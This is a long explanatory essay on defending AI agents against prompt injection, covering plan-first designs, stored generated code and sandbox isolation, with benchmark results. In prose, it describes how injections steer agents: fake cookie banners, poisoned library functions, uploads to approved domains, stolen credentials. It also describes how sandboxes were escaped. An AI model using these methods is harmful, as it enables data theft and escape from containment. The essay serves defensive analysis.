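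For some tasks, the agent's instructions are in the untrusted content. Piet and colleagues give the example of a user who asks an agent to complete all the action items in their emails. The agent has to read the emails to know what to do, and by then any of the senders can influence it. But if the user asks it to tell their regular collaborators about a holiday, the agent can write the program first. It doesn't know in advance who the collaborators are or how many there are, but it can write a loop that finds them and sends each one the same message. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues think most requests to an email assistant are like the holiday request.

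Programming often can't be fully planned in advance. *Architecting Secure AI Agents* (2026) points out that one failed test might require changing a single boundary check, while another might require reorganising how parts of a program wait for each other. A planner can't prepare a branch for every bug it might find. The paper argues that general-purpose agents will have to change their plans as they work, and that researchers should look for secure ways for them to do so.

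It makes a similar argument about fixed rules for data. CaMeL requires the recipient of a payment to come from the user's request. This prevents an injection from redirecting the money, but it also blocks some legitimate payments, and an injection can still raise the amount.

### Benchmark results for working systems

A benchmark can make fixed plans look good or useless, depending on how many of its tasks need replanning. The best-known test of injection defences, AgentDojo, has agents use simulated applications such as banking and travel booking. Li, Wen and colleagues (2026), in *AgentDyn*, found that only 6 of its 97 tasks required any replanning. They wrote 60 new tasks that all did, with helpful instructions along the way, such as a checkout page that tells the agent to log in first. They then combined the tasks with injections to make 560 attacks. Some of their results were:

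| Defence | Tasks completed without an attack | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|---|
| None | 53.3% | 37.8% |
| Choosing the permitted tools at the start | 8.3% | 4.2% |
| CaMeL (fixed program) | 0% | 0% |
| DRIFT (initial plan that can change after a check) | 30.0% | 0.8% |
| Meta SecAlign (model trained to resist injections) | 55.0% | 9.0% |

Meta SecAlign is itself a model, while the other rows use GPT-4o. CaMeL also completed no tasks with the three other models in the main comparison.

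CaMeL's perfect security means little here because it completed no tasks. Dongol notes that a monitor that refuses every call is secure by definition, so task success needs a separate test. But the zero completion rate exaggerates the problem, because Li and colleagues chose only tasks that a fixed plan would struggle with. Some of the obstacles, such as having to log in, are also predictable, and a more careful planner could have included a branch for them. The attacks were simple and came from a standard template, so the trained model's 9% could be much higher against an attacker who adapts.

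On AgentDojo itself, planning first works much better. *SPA* (2026) describes an agent that completed 53.0% of tasks, with at most 0.4% of attacks succeeding. The four successful attacks, out of 949, were all on a single banking task. Adding rules about where data may go stopped those four but reduced task success to 29.0%. About half of the runs ended early, usually because a plan passed an untrusted tool's output to a more sensitive tool. That is a large loss of task success for stopping four attacks, although the rules might be more useful against attacks designed to manipulate data.

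Other systems show a similar drop in completed tasks. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) reports that on AgentDojo's 21 tasks that use the messaging service Slack, a system called TypeGuard fell from 15 completed tasks to 8 when its data rules were on. CaMeL completed 7 under the same conditions. On these benchmarks, fixing the program in advance therefore seems to reduce task completion much less than controlling the data that moves through it.

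Writing the whole program in advance is harder for an agent that operates a computer through its screen, because it can't see which windows are open when it makes its plan. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026), a planner wrote a complete program for each task, and quarantined models looked at the screen, checked conditions and found buttons. The programs averaged 213 lines and 40 branches, compared with 52 lines and fewer than 4 branches for CaMeL's programs on AgentDojo. About half of each program was alternatives that went unused in a given run.

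These branches made a large difference. On 60 OSWorld benchmark tasks that the screen-reading model UI-TARS had already solved without protection, telling the planner to look, check and only then act raised success within three attempts from 18% to 58%. On the 109 tasks that Claude Sonnet 4.5 had solved without protection, the protected system solved 57% within five attempts, but only 28% on the first. Foerster and colleagues present the 57% as the share of performance that their design retains, but a user who gets one attempt should expect considerably less.

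The quality of the planner mattered more than the choice of screen-reading model. Three very different screen-reading models scored within about three percentage points of each other. The best of nine planners, GPT-5, solved 12 of a set of 17 tasks. All of these planners are now old, and current models would probably write better programs. The design used 1.88 times as many tokens as the unprotected agent. A variant that called the planner again at every step, without showing it the screen, used 29.6 times as many and succeeded about as often.

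Foerster and colleagues also found an attack, which they call branch steering, that follows the program's own branches. The program for virtually every web browser task includes a routine for dealing with cookie notices. The attacker buys a banner advertisement that looks like a cookie notice. The quarantined model gives the position of the advertisement's button, and the program clicks it and lands on the attacker's site, even though its only operation here is clicking a button, not visiting that site. Piet and colleagues want to remove this weakness by planning with named functions instead of clicks.

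Checking the screen against the page's underlying code stopped the attack with one type of banner but not another. Having other models confirm each answer more than tripled token use, and an advertisement with subtly altered pixels still fooled them. *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (2026) presents COBRA, a newer system built to resist such attacks. With up to five attempts per task, it completed 36.8% of 361 computer tasks, compared with 23.5% for an ordinary agent. But COBRA used GPT-5 as its planner, while the ordinary agent used only a small vision model, so the difference doesn't show that planning in advance improves performance.

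## Generating code in advance and running it as reviewed software

When a model writes a program for a single request, the program runs once and nobody has much reason to test it. If the sales manager wants the same report every week, the model can write the program once, staff can test and correct it, and later runs can reuse the stored version. Testing can then catch an error such as a wrong recipient before the program sends its first email.

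The stored program works like a fixed tool, except that a model wrote it. A schedule can start it, or an agent can call it and specify the quarter. No model reads the sales rows during a run unless the program calls one, so the customer's note can't affect what the program does. The note is still dangerous if the model reads it while writing the program.

### From a specification to a stored program

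*Compiled AI* describes a system for routine business tasks, particularly in healthcare administration. It works like this:

1. Staff write a specification in YAML, a plain-text format for structured data. It lists the inputs, the steps and the rules for each decision.
2. Ordinary software picks a template that developers have already tested, such as one for processing records in batches. It adds ready-made modules for database access, web requests or notifications, and written rules on matters such as patient privacy.
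3. A model writes only the missing business logic, in functions of 20 to 50 lines.
4. The system puts the parts together and runs four checks. If the code fails one, the model gets the errors and tries again.
5. Code that passes goes into use, and no model decides what happens next from then on.

For the sales report, the four checks might catch these mistakes:

| Check | How it works | Possible mistake in the sales program |
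|---|---|---|
| Security | Scanners look for known dangerous patterns | A region name pasted into the text of a query |
| Syntax | Tools parse the code and check its types and style | Text added to a number |
| Execution | The code runs in a sandbox on test data | A crash on an order with no date |
| Accuracy | The system compares results with answers known to be right | Returned orders counted as sales |

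If a step needs judgement, the stored program can call a model with a fixed question and answer format. In one example, the program decides whether an insurer should pay for a diabetes and weight-loss drug. A model reads the patient's chart and returns four values: whether the patient has type 2 diabetes, a blood-sugar level, a body mass index (BMI), and whether earlier treatments failed. Ordinary code then approves the drug for patients who have type 2 diabetes, and for patients with a BMI of at least 30 whose earlier treatments failed.

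The specification for this example also requires the BMI to be between 10 and 100, but the printed program doesn't check this. It does check whether the blood-sugar level is plausible, although the coverage rule never uses that level. The BMI check may be in the extraction function, which the paper doesn't print. If the check is missing, the program would still pass every test in which the patients had BMIs in that range.

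### Results on function calls and invoices

In a test with Claude Opus 4.5 on 400 function-calling tasks from the Berkeley leaderboard, the system produced correct code for 384 (96%). The code for the other 16 ran without errors but gave wrong results, and only the accuracy check detected them. A company with no known answers to compare against would have put all 16 into use. For the sales report, someone therefore has to supply at least one quarter's totals that the finance department has already confirmed.

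The second test used 5,680 invoices with poor scans and many different layouts. Code that didn't call a model found only 20.3% of key fields, such as the customer's name and the total. Code that called a model to extract the fields found 80.0%, the same as prompting the model directly, and did better on individual line items, with 80.4% compared with 74.5%. Its median time was shorter, at 2.7 seconds compared with 6.3, but its mean was 10.3 seconds because about a tenth of the invoices needed retries.

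The design reduces the attack surface more for the function-calling tasks than for invoice processing. In the function-calling tasks, no model runs after the code is finished, so an attacker has no model to inject instructions into. In invoice processing, a model reads every invoice, and the invoices come from outsiders. A malicious invoice can get the wrong amount into the accounts, but it can't add an operation to the program.

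The security check was less reliable than the accuracy check. It caught 15 of 20 deliberately vulnerable programs and raised no false alarms on 20 harmless ones. The generated code was also more complicated, averaging 23.8 on a standard measure of branching, compared with 8 for human code. That makes it harder for staff to find vulnerabilities that the security check misses.

### How many runs repay the cost

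Generating the code took about 9,600 tokens, and running it took none. To find how many runs repay this, divide 9,600 by the tokens that each run would otherwise have used:

| Alternative | Tokens per run | Runs needed to repay 9,600 tokens |
|---|---|---|
| One direct call to the model | 552 | 18 |
| LangChain (agent framework) | 740 | 13 |
| AutoGen | 805 | 12 |

*Compiled AI* rounds the first result down to 17, but 17 direct calls use only 9,384 tokens. After 1,000 runs, direct calls would have used 57 times as many tokens as the stored code.

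If each run saves 552 tokens, a weekly sales report would take about four months to save as many tokens as were used to generate its code. A real sales agent makes several model calls per report, so it would probably take less time. But this estimate leaves out the work of writing the specification, supplying the known answers and reviewing the code. At the prices the paper uses, a direct call costs about 2.15 cents. If a reviewer costs $60 an hour, an hour of review costs as much as 2,800 calls, or 54 years of weekly reports. That cost is negligible for a company that processes a million claims a month. For the sales report, the token savings are tiny, so the reason to review the code has to be accuracy or security.

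### Turning past runs into workflows

If no one can write the procedure down as a specification, developers can start from traces, which are records of what an agent did, including its reasoning, tool calls and their results. García-Carrasco, Sanchis and colleagues (2026), in *Compiling Agent Traces into Typed Workflows for Cheaper and Faster Execution*, gave a compiler agent 14 to 17 successful traces for each of three tasks in AppWorld, a simulated set of everyday apps.

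The compiler turned each set into a graph with up to three types of step. An "execute" step runs code, a "decide" step has a model answer one limited question, usually by choosing from listed options, and a "generate" step has a model produce free text or another open-ended value. The software that runs the graph rejects any choice that isn't on the list, and free text can never determine which step comes next. The researchers then tested each workflow on ten cases the compiler hadn't seen:

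| Task | Solved by workflow | Solved by agent | Model calls per run (workflow / agent) | Runs to repay |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Follow all artists in a genre with enough followers | 10 of 10 | 10 of 10 | 1 / 9.3 | 50 |
| Move one alarm and disable the others | 10 of 10 | 9 of 10 | 2 / 7.7 | 41 |
| Remove songs released before or after a given year | 10 of 10 | 10 of 10 | 0 / 13.3 | 31 |

The artist workflow needed a model to match the requested genre to one in the app. The alarm workflow used a model to tell which alarm the user meant and whether to move it earlier or later. In the song workflow, code could read the year and the comparison directly from the request. A typical run cost 98 times less than the agent's and took 0.6 seconds instead of 46.

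The repayment figures include the cost of producing the traces. The researchers could generate only 24 to 27 distinct cases of each task, so none of the workflows would have paid for itself if each case had come up only once.

The new cases had different users, songs and dates, but every request had the same wording as one in the traces, so the results don't show how the workflows would handle new wording. When the compiler had only one trace, it treated details of that case as part of the procedure, and the alarm workflow solved four of ten cases and the song workflow two. With three traces, both again solved all ten.

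*FlashScript* (Sabouri, Hasanbeig and colleagues, 2026) found the same weakness in programs based on a single run. Programs solved all 108 unseen cases of 12 data-analysis tasks when the model that wrote them also had a template showing which parts of the request could vary. Programs based on the run alone did worse.

A successful run can also contain a bad method. In one example, the user asked about percentage growth and the agent compared totals instead. Both methods happened to give the right answer, so the grader accepted the run. Written instructions based on that run kept the shortcut, and an agent that followed them was right 67% of the time, compared with 87% for an agent with no instructions. The model writing the stored program corrected the shortcut, but only because the researchers had told it to plan before writing code.

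Compilers can make mistakes in their own tests too. In an early experiment by García-Carrasco and colleagues, the compiler built a copy of the artist data from the traces, ran its workflow on the copy and reported success. The researchers had to add a rule that every value must come from the real system. *Natural-Language Workflows Are Not Software Yet* (Xu, Guo and colleagues, 2026) tested a related compiler that converts written procedures into workflows for agents to carry out. Removing the step that checked the workflow against the original procedure lowered the success rate by 16 percentage points.

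### When an outside service changes

Stored code can stop working even if nobody has changed it. In *SkillShift-Bench*, Chen, Zhou and Li (2026) summarise earlier research on recorded website tests, which found that most break because a page's layout changes or an element gets a new label, rather than because the site removed a function. In their own tests on GitLab, WordPress and the shop software Magento, agents' stored skills also became less reliable when the site changed, especially when unexpected pop-ups appeared, even though every task was still possible.

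How often a library breaks depends partly on what its functions do. A function that clicks a particular button finds it using a selector, which is a description of an item on the page, and a redesign can make that selector stop working. Piet and colleagues recommend larger functions, such as one that searches a shop's entire catalogue. When the page changes, someone still has to repair the function, but the programs that call it don't need to change.

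A function that is too large can hide important choices. One example is a `checkout` function that silently picks the shipping and payment method. A stored `send_sales_report()` with no parameters could hide who receives the report and whether returns count as sales.

Libraries also have to account for each site's peculiarities. One shop in WebArena expects percent signs between search words instead of spaces, and the forum requires a special header with every request. Official interfaces have gaps. GitLab's, for example, has no function to generate the token that an RSS feed needs. Developers can fill such gaps by automating a browser, but that code depends on the site's pages, so it is the most likely to break.

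*Benchmarking Real-Time Question Answering via Executable Code Workflows* (Zhou, Gao and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent that writes scripts to read current information from websites. The agent returned a script in 71% of attempts, and 96.3% of those scripts passed a manual check. It can also repair its scripts when websites change.

A repair agent can only fix a failure that someone or something detects. The researchers told their agent not to write code that hides errors, but a script can give a wrong answer without raising an error. One of their scripts searches a theatre's online calendar and reports that there are no performances tomorrow if it finds none. If a redesign kept it from finding any dates, the code as printed would give the same answer. The sales program will crash if someone renames the `amount` column, but if the western office starts recording sales in another currency,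 it will draw the wrong chart without raising an error.

Developers can handle repairs in several ways:

- **A person edits the code.** In *Agentic Compilation* (2026), a model writes a plan for automating a website, and an operator reviews it before it runs. If a selector breaks later, the operator can replace it by hand. No model has to read the changed page, and only one line needs checking.
- **A model writes the program again.** The new version may be very different. When García-Carrasco and colleagues compiled the artist traces three times, they got workflows of 20, 15 and 19 steps. All three worked, but a reviewer would have had to read each from the beginning.
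- **A repair agent changes the code until the tests pass.** *Practical Limits of Autonomous Test Repair* (2026) found that without a separate standard of correctness, an agent can't reliably tell a real repair from one that only appears to work. The agent should therefore have no permission to change the tests or the known answers.
- **A model adapts the steps during the run.** Chen and colleagues leave the stored skills alone and have a model rank the actions that seem possible on the current page. This can get past a changed layout, but the model again reads a live page just before choosing an action, so an injection can influence the choice.

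Whoever makes the repair, the company needs to know which version produced which result. The insurance program in *Compiled AI* records its version number with every decision, so staff who find a mistake can look up the other decisions it affected. For the sales report, the company could keep the data from a few quarters with confirmed totals and check that every new version reproduces those totals. It could also add a new function to the library only after the function passes the tests of the programs that call it, as in *LLM-as-Code* (Qi, Zhang and colleagues, 2026).

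Model calls inside stored code need different tests. Sabouri and colleagues recommend repeating each call several times, because the answers can vary, and checking that the surrounding code handles every answer the format allows. If the sales program uses a model to identify complaints about late delivery, staff should repeat these tests whenever they switch to a new model, even if the code hasn't changed.

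### Requests the stored code doesn't cover

The manager may ask for something no stored program does, or an existing program may meet a case its authors didn't expect. The workflow in *TraceCompiler* (El Yadouni and Li, 2026) stops in the second situation. El Yadouni and Li used three past runs of requesting money on Venmo, a payment app. They built the workflow from two runs and tested it on the third, holding out each run in turn. Two tests succeeded completely. In the other, the recipient wasn't in the user's Venmo friends list, and neither of the two runs used to build the workflow had looked anyone up in the phone's contacts, so the workflow stopped without requesting money from anyone. Across the three tests, it passed 15 of 21 checks, with the help of hand-written code for reading the requests.

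Their compiler also stopped without producing a workflow for updating a music playlist, because the traces didn't show whether the agent was adding songs or removing them. A person could have settled this with one sentence, but a wrong guess would have done the opposite of what the user intended.

A router looks for a stored workflow similar to each new request and passes the request to a general agent if it finds none. El Yadouni and Li set it to require a close match, since a missed match only sends the request to the general agent, while a false match could run the wrong payment procedure. They didn't measure how often it routes requests correctly.

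An agent that takes over when the library doesn't cover a request needs reduced permissions, as with programs written for a single request. Otherwise, the original attack will work on every such request. The company could instead have the system refuse these requests until staff approve a new program. This is safer, but the manager may wait days for a chart the old agent could have drawn in a minute.

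### Poisoned functions

The argument for delegation assumes that dividing the work removes more exposure to attack than the added parts create. Here those parts are the model that writes the code, the material it reads, the library and the repair process. Piet and colleagues describe a possible attack in which a model building a library for a shop reads live pages, including a review that contains an injection. It then writes a `get_reviews` function that also sends data to the attacker. Every later program that calls the function leaks data, even if the model that wrote that program never saw anything untrusted.

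The sales program has the same weakness if the model prints some real rows to see what they look like. The customer's note could get the model to add the outside address to the stored code, which would then send out the customer list every week, even after someone deleted the note from the database. Hiding the database from the model isn't enough if the model works from traces, because a trace contains whatever the agent read, including customers' notes.

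Whether this is worse than the original danger depends on how often the model writes code and how much harm each leak does. Suppose the note has a 1% chance of succeeding each time a model writes code after reading it. An agent that writes new code for each of 52 weekly reports has a 41% chance of sending at least one bad email during the year. If the model writes the code once, the chance is 1%, but a successful attack affects all 52 reports. The average number of bad emails is about 0.5 in both cases. For a customer list, the first leak does most of the damage, so the stored program is much safer. For payments, where the attacker gains from every run, storing the code reduces the average loss only if someone catches the attack. Each repair in which a model reads real rows adds another 1% chance of a successful attack, and a compromised function that many programs share can do more damage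 than one compromised report.

Poisoned code can also spread. *EVOMAL* (Wu, Shi et al., 2026) found that coding agents that build their own libraries copied harmful code from planted examples into new tools on 20 to 42% of relevant tasks. The copies could survive after someone removed the originals.

Piet and colleagues propose three checks for generated libraries. The first is to build them from trusted material, such as the website's own source code or recordings of its network traffic from test accounts filled with known data. The model could write the sales program from the column names and some invented rows. This keeps the note away from the model, but invented rows won't contain surprises such as "W" for "West", so staff may have to describe those problems themselves. A developer building a library for someone else's website may lack the full source code or a suitable test account.

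Static analysis, which examines code without running it, can check that a function does only what its description declares. If `get_reviews` should only read data, any request that writes or sends something is suspicious. This check works less well for a function that is supposed to send email, because an extra recipient doesn't add a new kind of effect, so the analysis would have to compare the recipients with an approved list. General scanners are even weaker. In tests by Wu and colleagues, small rewrites of harmful tools greatly reduced the share that Bandit, one of the scanners *Compiled AI* uses, caught.

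The remaining check is a human audit of each function before it enters the library. Wu and colleagues proved that if agents can retrieve only functions that a trusted curator has signed, harmful copies written by agents almost never get back into use. The proof doesn't cover harmful functions that the curator signs by mistake, so the protection depends on reviewers paying attention to every function.

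All of these checks are practical for one sales program. Staff can supply invented rows, restrict the recipients, give the program a database account that can't read the customer list, and read the code. With those checks, the added parts probably expose less than the unrestricted agent did. A library for hundreds of websites is harder to check because every site update can require new code and another audit. Piet and colleagues call validation on that scale an open problem, and they don't test the checks they propose. An automatic repair agent would make the updates manageable, but if it learns about each change from the live site, it reads the same reviews and advertisements that could have poisoned the original library.

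## Running the code on a separate machine

Reviewed programs work well for a weekly report. For an unexpected request, a company can instead let the agent write any program and limit what that program can access. The code runs in a sandbox, often on a different computer, and the database and mail logins stay outside it. The customer's note can still influence the code, but the code should have access to little worth stealing and no way to send it out.

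This design depends almost entirely on the generated code running with less authority than the undivided agent had. The size of the reduction depends on which files the developer shares with the sandbox, which addresses the code can contact, and what happens to the files it produces.

### How Managed Agents separates the parts

Anthropic's *Scaling Managed Agents* describes a hosted service for agents that work on long tasks. In its first version, the harness, the model's code and the session record shared one container. A container is a group of processes that has its own files but shares the kernel, the core of the operating system, with the rest of the computer. This design was easy to build, but if the container failed, the session was lost. Engineers also struggled to tell why a session had stopped, because a bug in the harness, a lost network packet and a failed container all looked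 the same from outside. To investigate, they would have had to open a shell in a container that often held a customer's data.

Anthropic then split the system into three parts. The session is a log of everything that has happened, to which the system only ever adds entries. The other two parts are the harness and the sandbox where the model's code runs. With this design, the sales report would run like this:

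1. The harness records the manager's request in the log and sends it to the model. No sandbox exists yet.
2. The model writes a program. The harness creates a container from a standard recipe and sends it the program through `execute(name, input)`, the same kind of call it uses for every other tool. The call returns text.
3. The harness adds that text to the log and to the model's prompt, and the loop continues.
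4. If the container dies, the harness gives the model an ordinary tool error. If the model tries again, the harness can create a new container.
5. If the harness itself crashes, a new one reads the log and continues from the last entry.

Developers should plan for the limits of recovery. A new container starts from the recipe, so files that existed only in the old one are probably gone. The model also may not be able to tell from the error how far the old program got. If the program had already mailed the chart when the container died, a second attempt could mail it again, which is another reason to keep mailing in a separate tool.

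The split also made sessions start faster. Previously, every session waited for a container, even if it never ran any code. Now the harness creates one only when the model asks for it. The median wait for the model's first token fell by roughly 60%, and the 95th-percentile wait fell by more than 90%. These figures measure how soon an agent begins to respond, not how quickly it finishes or how often it succeeds. A session that needs to run code still waits for its container, but later. Anthropic gives no figures for how often sessions recover from a crash.

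The split also helped customers with data in their own private networks, who previously had to connect those networks to Anthropic's or run the harness themselves. The drawback is that a model with several places to run code has to decide where to send each job. Anthropic says earlier models couldn't do this, which is partly why it began with a single container.

The change that most affected security involved access tokens, the secret strings that let a program use a service. In the first version, the tokens were in the same container as the model's code, so an attacker only had to use an injection to get the model to read its own settings, and could then use the tokens to start new, unrestricted sessions. Anthropic could have given the tokens narrower rights, but that would have meant guessing what an increasingly capable model couldn't do with a limited token.

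Anthropic instead put the tokens where the sandbox can't reach them. The system uses a code repository's token to copy the repository while setting up the sandbox, and it configures Git so that later uploads and downloads work without the agent handling the token. Tokens for other services stay in a vault. When the model calls a tool, a proxy (a program that passes requests on) fetches the right token and contacts the service without exposing the token to the harness.

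An attacker who can't steal a hidden token can still use it through the agent. If the proxy accepts any query for the sales database, an agent steered by the attacker can request the customer list without knowing the password.

### Three places to run the code

Anthropic's containment report compares how three of the company's products are contained. One of them, the chatbot at claude.ai, runs code in a container on Anthropic's servers. Software called gVisor separates the code from the server's kernel, and the container's files last for one session. The code never runs on the user's computer, so Anthropic worked mainly on protecting its own servers and isolating customers from one another. The drawback is that the code can't access the user's own files or keep a workspace between sessions.

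Claude Code runs on a programmer's computer because it needs the files and tools there. At launch, it could read files freely but had to ask before writing a file, running a command or using the network. Users soon paid less attention to these requests, so Anthropic added a sandbox built from features of the operating system. By default, commands in the sandbox can read files, but they can write only in the project folder and can't connect to the network. A more privileged process outside the sandbox decides whether to enforce it for each command. A persuasive prompt injection or a careless approval can get that process to run a command without the sandbox.

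Cowork is for office workers, few of whom can judge whether a shell command is safe, so Anthropic wanted a boundary that didn't depend on their approval. The first version of Cowork ran in a virtual machine (a simulated computer with its own kernel and files) on the user's computer. The user picks a folder to share with it, which can be read-only, writable, or writable without permission to delete. Passwords stay in the main system's keychain, and the virtual machine gets a limited token that works for one session.

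To compare these arrangements, suppose that the sales agent's harness exports last quarter's orders, with customers' notes, to a file. The model writes a program that draws the chart, and the harness sends the chart with the fixed `email_chart` tool and its six permitted recipients. The model prints some rows, follows the note and writes a program to steal the customer list. That program could reach the following:

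| Where the program runs | Files it can read | Files it can change | Network | Logins |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Company server, unrestricted | Everything the server account can read | Everything the server account can change | Any address | Database and mail |
| Server container | The order file | Temporary files in the container | None, if the developer blocks it | None |
| Local sandbox with Claude Code's defaults | Most of the manager's files | The project folder | None without approval | Any saved in readable files |
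| Virtual machine, as Anthropic describes Cowork's | The shared folder and Cowork's settings folder | The same, unless read-only | Approved domains | A limited token for the session |

The theft fails in the server container because the container has no customer list, mail account or outside connection. The program can still draw false totals in the chart or write customers' names from the order file into it. The premise about authority is clearly true here.

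Running the program in the local sandbox changes its authority rather than simply reducing it. The program loses access to the database and the mail account, but it can read the manager's private documents and any passwords saved in ordinary files, which it couldn't do on the company server. The blocked network prevents it from sending those files directly, but the program could print their contents into the model's prompt or draw them into the chart.

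In an internal exercise at Anthropic in February 2026, a researcher tricked an employee into giving Claude Code a prompt that looked like routine set-up instructions. One step was to read the employee's cloud credentials and send them to an outside address. The model did so in 24 of 25 attempts. The instructions came from the user, so the model's safeguards had nothing unusual to detect. Anthropic concludes that only limits on network access and on which files the model could read would have stopped the theft.

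A developer might also put the database login in the container to avoid exporting a new file for every request. The program can then read the customer list again, no matter how well the container protects the server.

### Why Cowork's agent loop left the virtual machine

At first, Cowork's whole agent loop ran inside the virtual machine. This gave it a security advantage over Claude Code, because no process outside it was allowed to run a command without the sandbox. But if the virtual machine failed to start, the agent failed too, and the product froze without telling the user why.

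Anthropic moved the agent loop out of the virtual machine and left code execution inside it. If the virtual machine fails now, the model can still answer the user and help find the problem. Managed Agents became more reliable in the same way when its harness was moved out of the container. Anthropic says moving the loop had minimal impact on security, because the virtual machine still controls which files and networks the model's code can reach.

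This is a good argument about code, but an agent also has other tools. Anthropic also moved local MCP servers, the programs that connect an agent to other software on the computer, out of the virtual machine. They had been hard to audit there, broke when the virtual machine changed, and couldn't work with local databases. They are now like any other software the user installs, and administrators decide which ones to allow. If the sales agent's mail tool were one of these servers, the virtual machine wouldn't limit what it could send.

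### Approved addresses that leak data

Cowork's virtual machine could contact only approved domains, including `api.anthropic.com`, which the product needs to reach the model. An outside researcher showed that an attacker could add a file to the user's shared folder that contained hidden instructions and the key to the attacker's own Anthropic account. The model followed the instructions, read other files in the folder and uploaded them to that account. The network filter allowed the upload because the destination was an approved domain.

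The designers had wrongly assumed that data sent to an approved address was safe, when anyone can open an account there. In the repaired version, a proxy in the virtual machine passes a request to Anthropic only if the request carries that machine's own session token, so the attacker's key no longer works. The proxy has to run inside the virtual machine because Anthropic's servers can't tell Cowork's requests apart from any other customer's. A program that took complete control of the virtual machine might therefore be able to interfere with the proxy.

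Anthropic now thinks of an approved domain as a "capability grant", meaning that approving it permits everything the code can do there. Suppose the sales developer approves a public package site so that the model's program can install a charting library. If the site also accepts uploads, the program could publish the order file there. Even a service meant only for downloads can have a flaw. GitLab's *A sandbox is only as closed as what an AI agent can reach* (2026) describes how an OpenAI model under evaluation reached the internet through a vulnerable package service on its approved list.

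*A sandbox without a network boundary is only half a sandbox* (Tuttle, 2026) describes how Vercel, a cloud company, tries to prevent such leaks. Each customer's code runs in a small virtual machine, and a filter outside it checks every connection. When the code opens an encrypted connection, the filter reads the name of the requested site from the first message, which is unencrypted. If the site is on the approved list, the filter usually passes the rest of the traffic without reading it. A developer can change the list while the sandbox runs, for instance by allowing a package site during set-up and blocking it before the model's code starts.

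Two months later, the security company AIR reported a way around the filter. Smalley (2026) explains in *Sandbox vulnerability gives rogue AI agents a path to escape* that code in the sandbox could send an approved server a specially made digital certificate, a file normally used to prove identity. The certificate could cause that server to contact the attacker's server and pass information to it. Approved servers can make connections that don't pass through the filter, so controlling which servers the sandbox contacted did not control where its data went, as Vercel's design had assumed it would.

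Vercel had no patch when Smalley wrote on 13 October 2026, and AIR said the company didn't yet know how it would make one. AIR had found no sign that anyone had used the flaw in a real attack but couldn't rule it out. Tuttle had already listed the general method, turning a trusted package service into a relay, among the ways out of a sandbox.

The filter can also add a password or key to a request after the request leaves the sandbox, so the code never holds the credential. Tuttle notes that a developer can limit the key to certain operations, such as submitting results but not reading anything else. The key is protected only if the filter sends it to the right place. Docker Sandboxes, a product for running coding agents, recorded which destinations a developer had approved for each key but didn't check them again on later runs. According to SC Media's *Docker sandboxes vulnerability exposes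 developer API keys* (2026), someone who distributed a malicious update to an add-on could redirect requests to their own server, and Docker would attach the developer's key. The flaw affected keys for 13 services, including OpenAI and GitHub, and the logs didn't show that Docker had added a key. Docker fixed the flaw on 30 November 2026.

The sales developer can avoid most of these problems by installing the charting library in advance and then blocking every connection, because drawing a chart from a file needs no network. An agent that has to fetch current exchange rates or update a website can't work without a connection.

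### Files that other programs run

As with settings files, a program outside the sandbox may run what the agent writes inside it. Cohen, Lisichkin and Fogel (2026), in *The Week of Sandbox Escapes*, found this problem and related ones in four coding agents: Cursor, Codex, Gemini CLI and Google's Antigravity. The researchers work for the security company Pillar, which sells a product for monitoring such agents. Their seven findings fall into four groups:

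| What the design assumed | Why it was false | Products | Outcome |
|---|---|---|---|
| Files in the project folder can't affect the rest of the computer | Trusted programs outside the sandbox ran commands or programs from those files | Cursor (three findings), Antigravity (one) | Cursor fixed its three; Google downgraded the other |
| A command with a safe name is safe | `git show` looks as if it only reads, but some arguments have side effects | Codex | Fixed |
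| Restricting the agent's own process is enough | The agent could ask Docker, which runs outside the sandbox with greater privileges, to do the work | Codex, Cursor, Gemini CLI | Fixed |
| Blocking a list of dangerous operations is enough | The list left out system features that could start programs outside the sandbox | Antigravity | Google downgraded it |

Google accepted both of its findings as valid but judged them hard to exploit because the user would have to trust a malicious project or fall for a trick.

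In one of the Cursor attacks, the agent changed the copy of Python stored in the project folder, as the sandbox's rules allowed. An add-on for Python then ran that copy outside the sandbox while looking for versions of Python it could use. The add-on worked as intended, but its developers had designed it before coding agents existed.

Claude Code had a similar problem. When it started, it read a project's settings before asking whether the user trusted the folder, and those settings could contain a command to run automatically. A programmer who downloaded a stranger's project to review it could therefore run the stranger's command without agreeing to anything. Anthropic fixed this by having Claude Code read such settings only after the user agrees to trust the folder.

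Cohen and colleagues conclude that the damage an agent can do extends to everything it can write that the host later trusts. They recommend requiring approval when an agent changes a file that can start a program, sandboxing the helper programs as well, and recording which files the agent wrote so that other software can treat them differently from the user's own.

A server container avoids many of these attacks because the user's programs can't read its files until someone copies them out. Once copied, the files can be dangerous again. Suppose the company keeps its approved weekly report program in a shared folder where the sales agent's container can save charts. A steered agent could replace the approved program, and the next scheduled run would execute the new one with the database and mail logins. The developer can prevent this by having the harness copy out only an image file and put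 it in a folder that no programs are run from.

### Flaws in the isolation

In the attacks so far, the barrier around the code mostly worked as its developers intended. Anthropic wrote in May 2026 that established components such as gVisor and virtual machines had withstood attack, while its own network proxy had failed. It advised developers to be wary of anything they build themselves. Later events support that advice but also show that established components can fail.

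In July, researchers at Accomplish AI escaped from Cowork's virtual machine on Mac. The Next Web's *Anthropic's Claude Cowork could escape its local VM and read credentials* explains that the virtual machine was connected to the Mac's entire file system, but only the virtual machine's administrator account could use that connection. A flaw in the Linux kernel let the agent's code gain that account's powers. The code could then read and change files all over the Mac, including stored login keys.

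Anthropic had reported that nothing outside the shared folders was visible to the virtual machine. This was true of ordinary code there, but not of code that gained administrator privileges. The design would have been much safer if the virtual machine had never had access to the other files. Anthropic closed the researchers' report without a direct fix, though later versions of Cowork run code in the cloud by default. People who run code locally remain exposed unless they change the configuration.

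Another reported escape is weaker evidence. *Armadin details full sandbox escape in Claude Cowork but Anthropic disputes risk* (SiliconANGLE, 2026) describes an attack on the Windows version of Claude Cowork that ran commands as administrator in the sandbox and removed its network limits. Anthropic replied that the attacker would already need to be running code on the user's computer. Such an attacker has less need of the agent, although the attack could still give them access to whatever the agent is working on.

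Cloud sandboxes protect the user's computer, but they often run on the same server as other customers' code. *Critical PwnEscape Linux Kernel Vulnerability Lets Guest VMs Read Host Memory* (The Hacker News, October 2026) reported that code in one of Vercel's sandboxes could read the memory of the server beneath it, about 32 bytes with each network packet it sent. Working on his own machines, a researcher also used the flaw to take control of a server. The flaw came to light in Vercel's security challenge, but Vercel said no participant had shown they could read another customer's files or secrets. Linux developers have added a deliberately partial fix.

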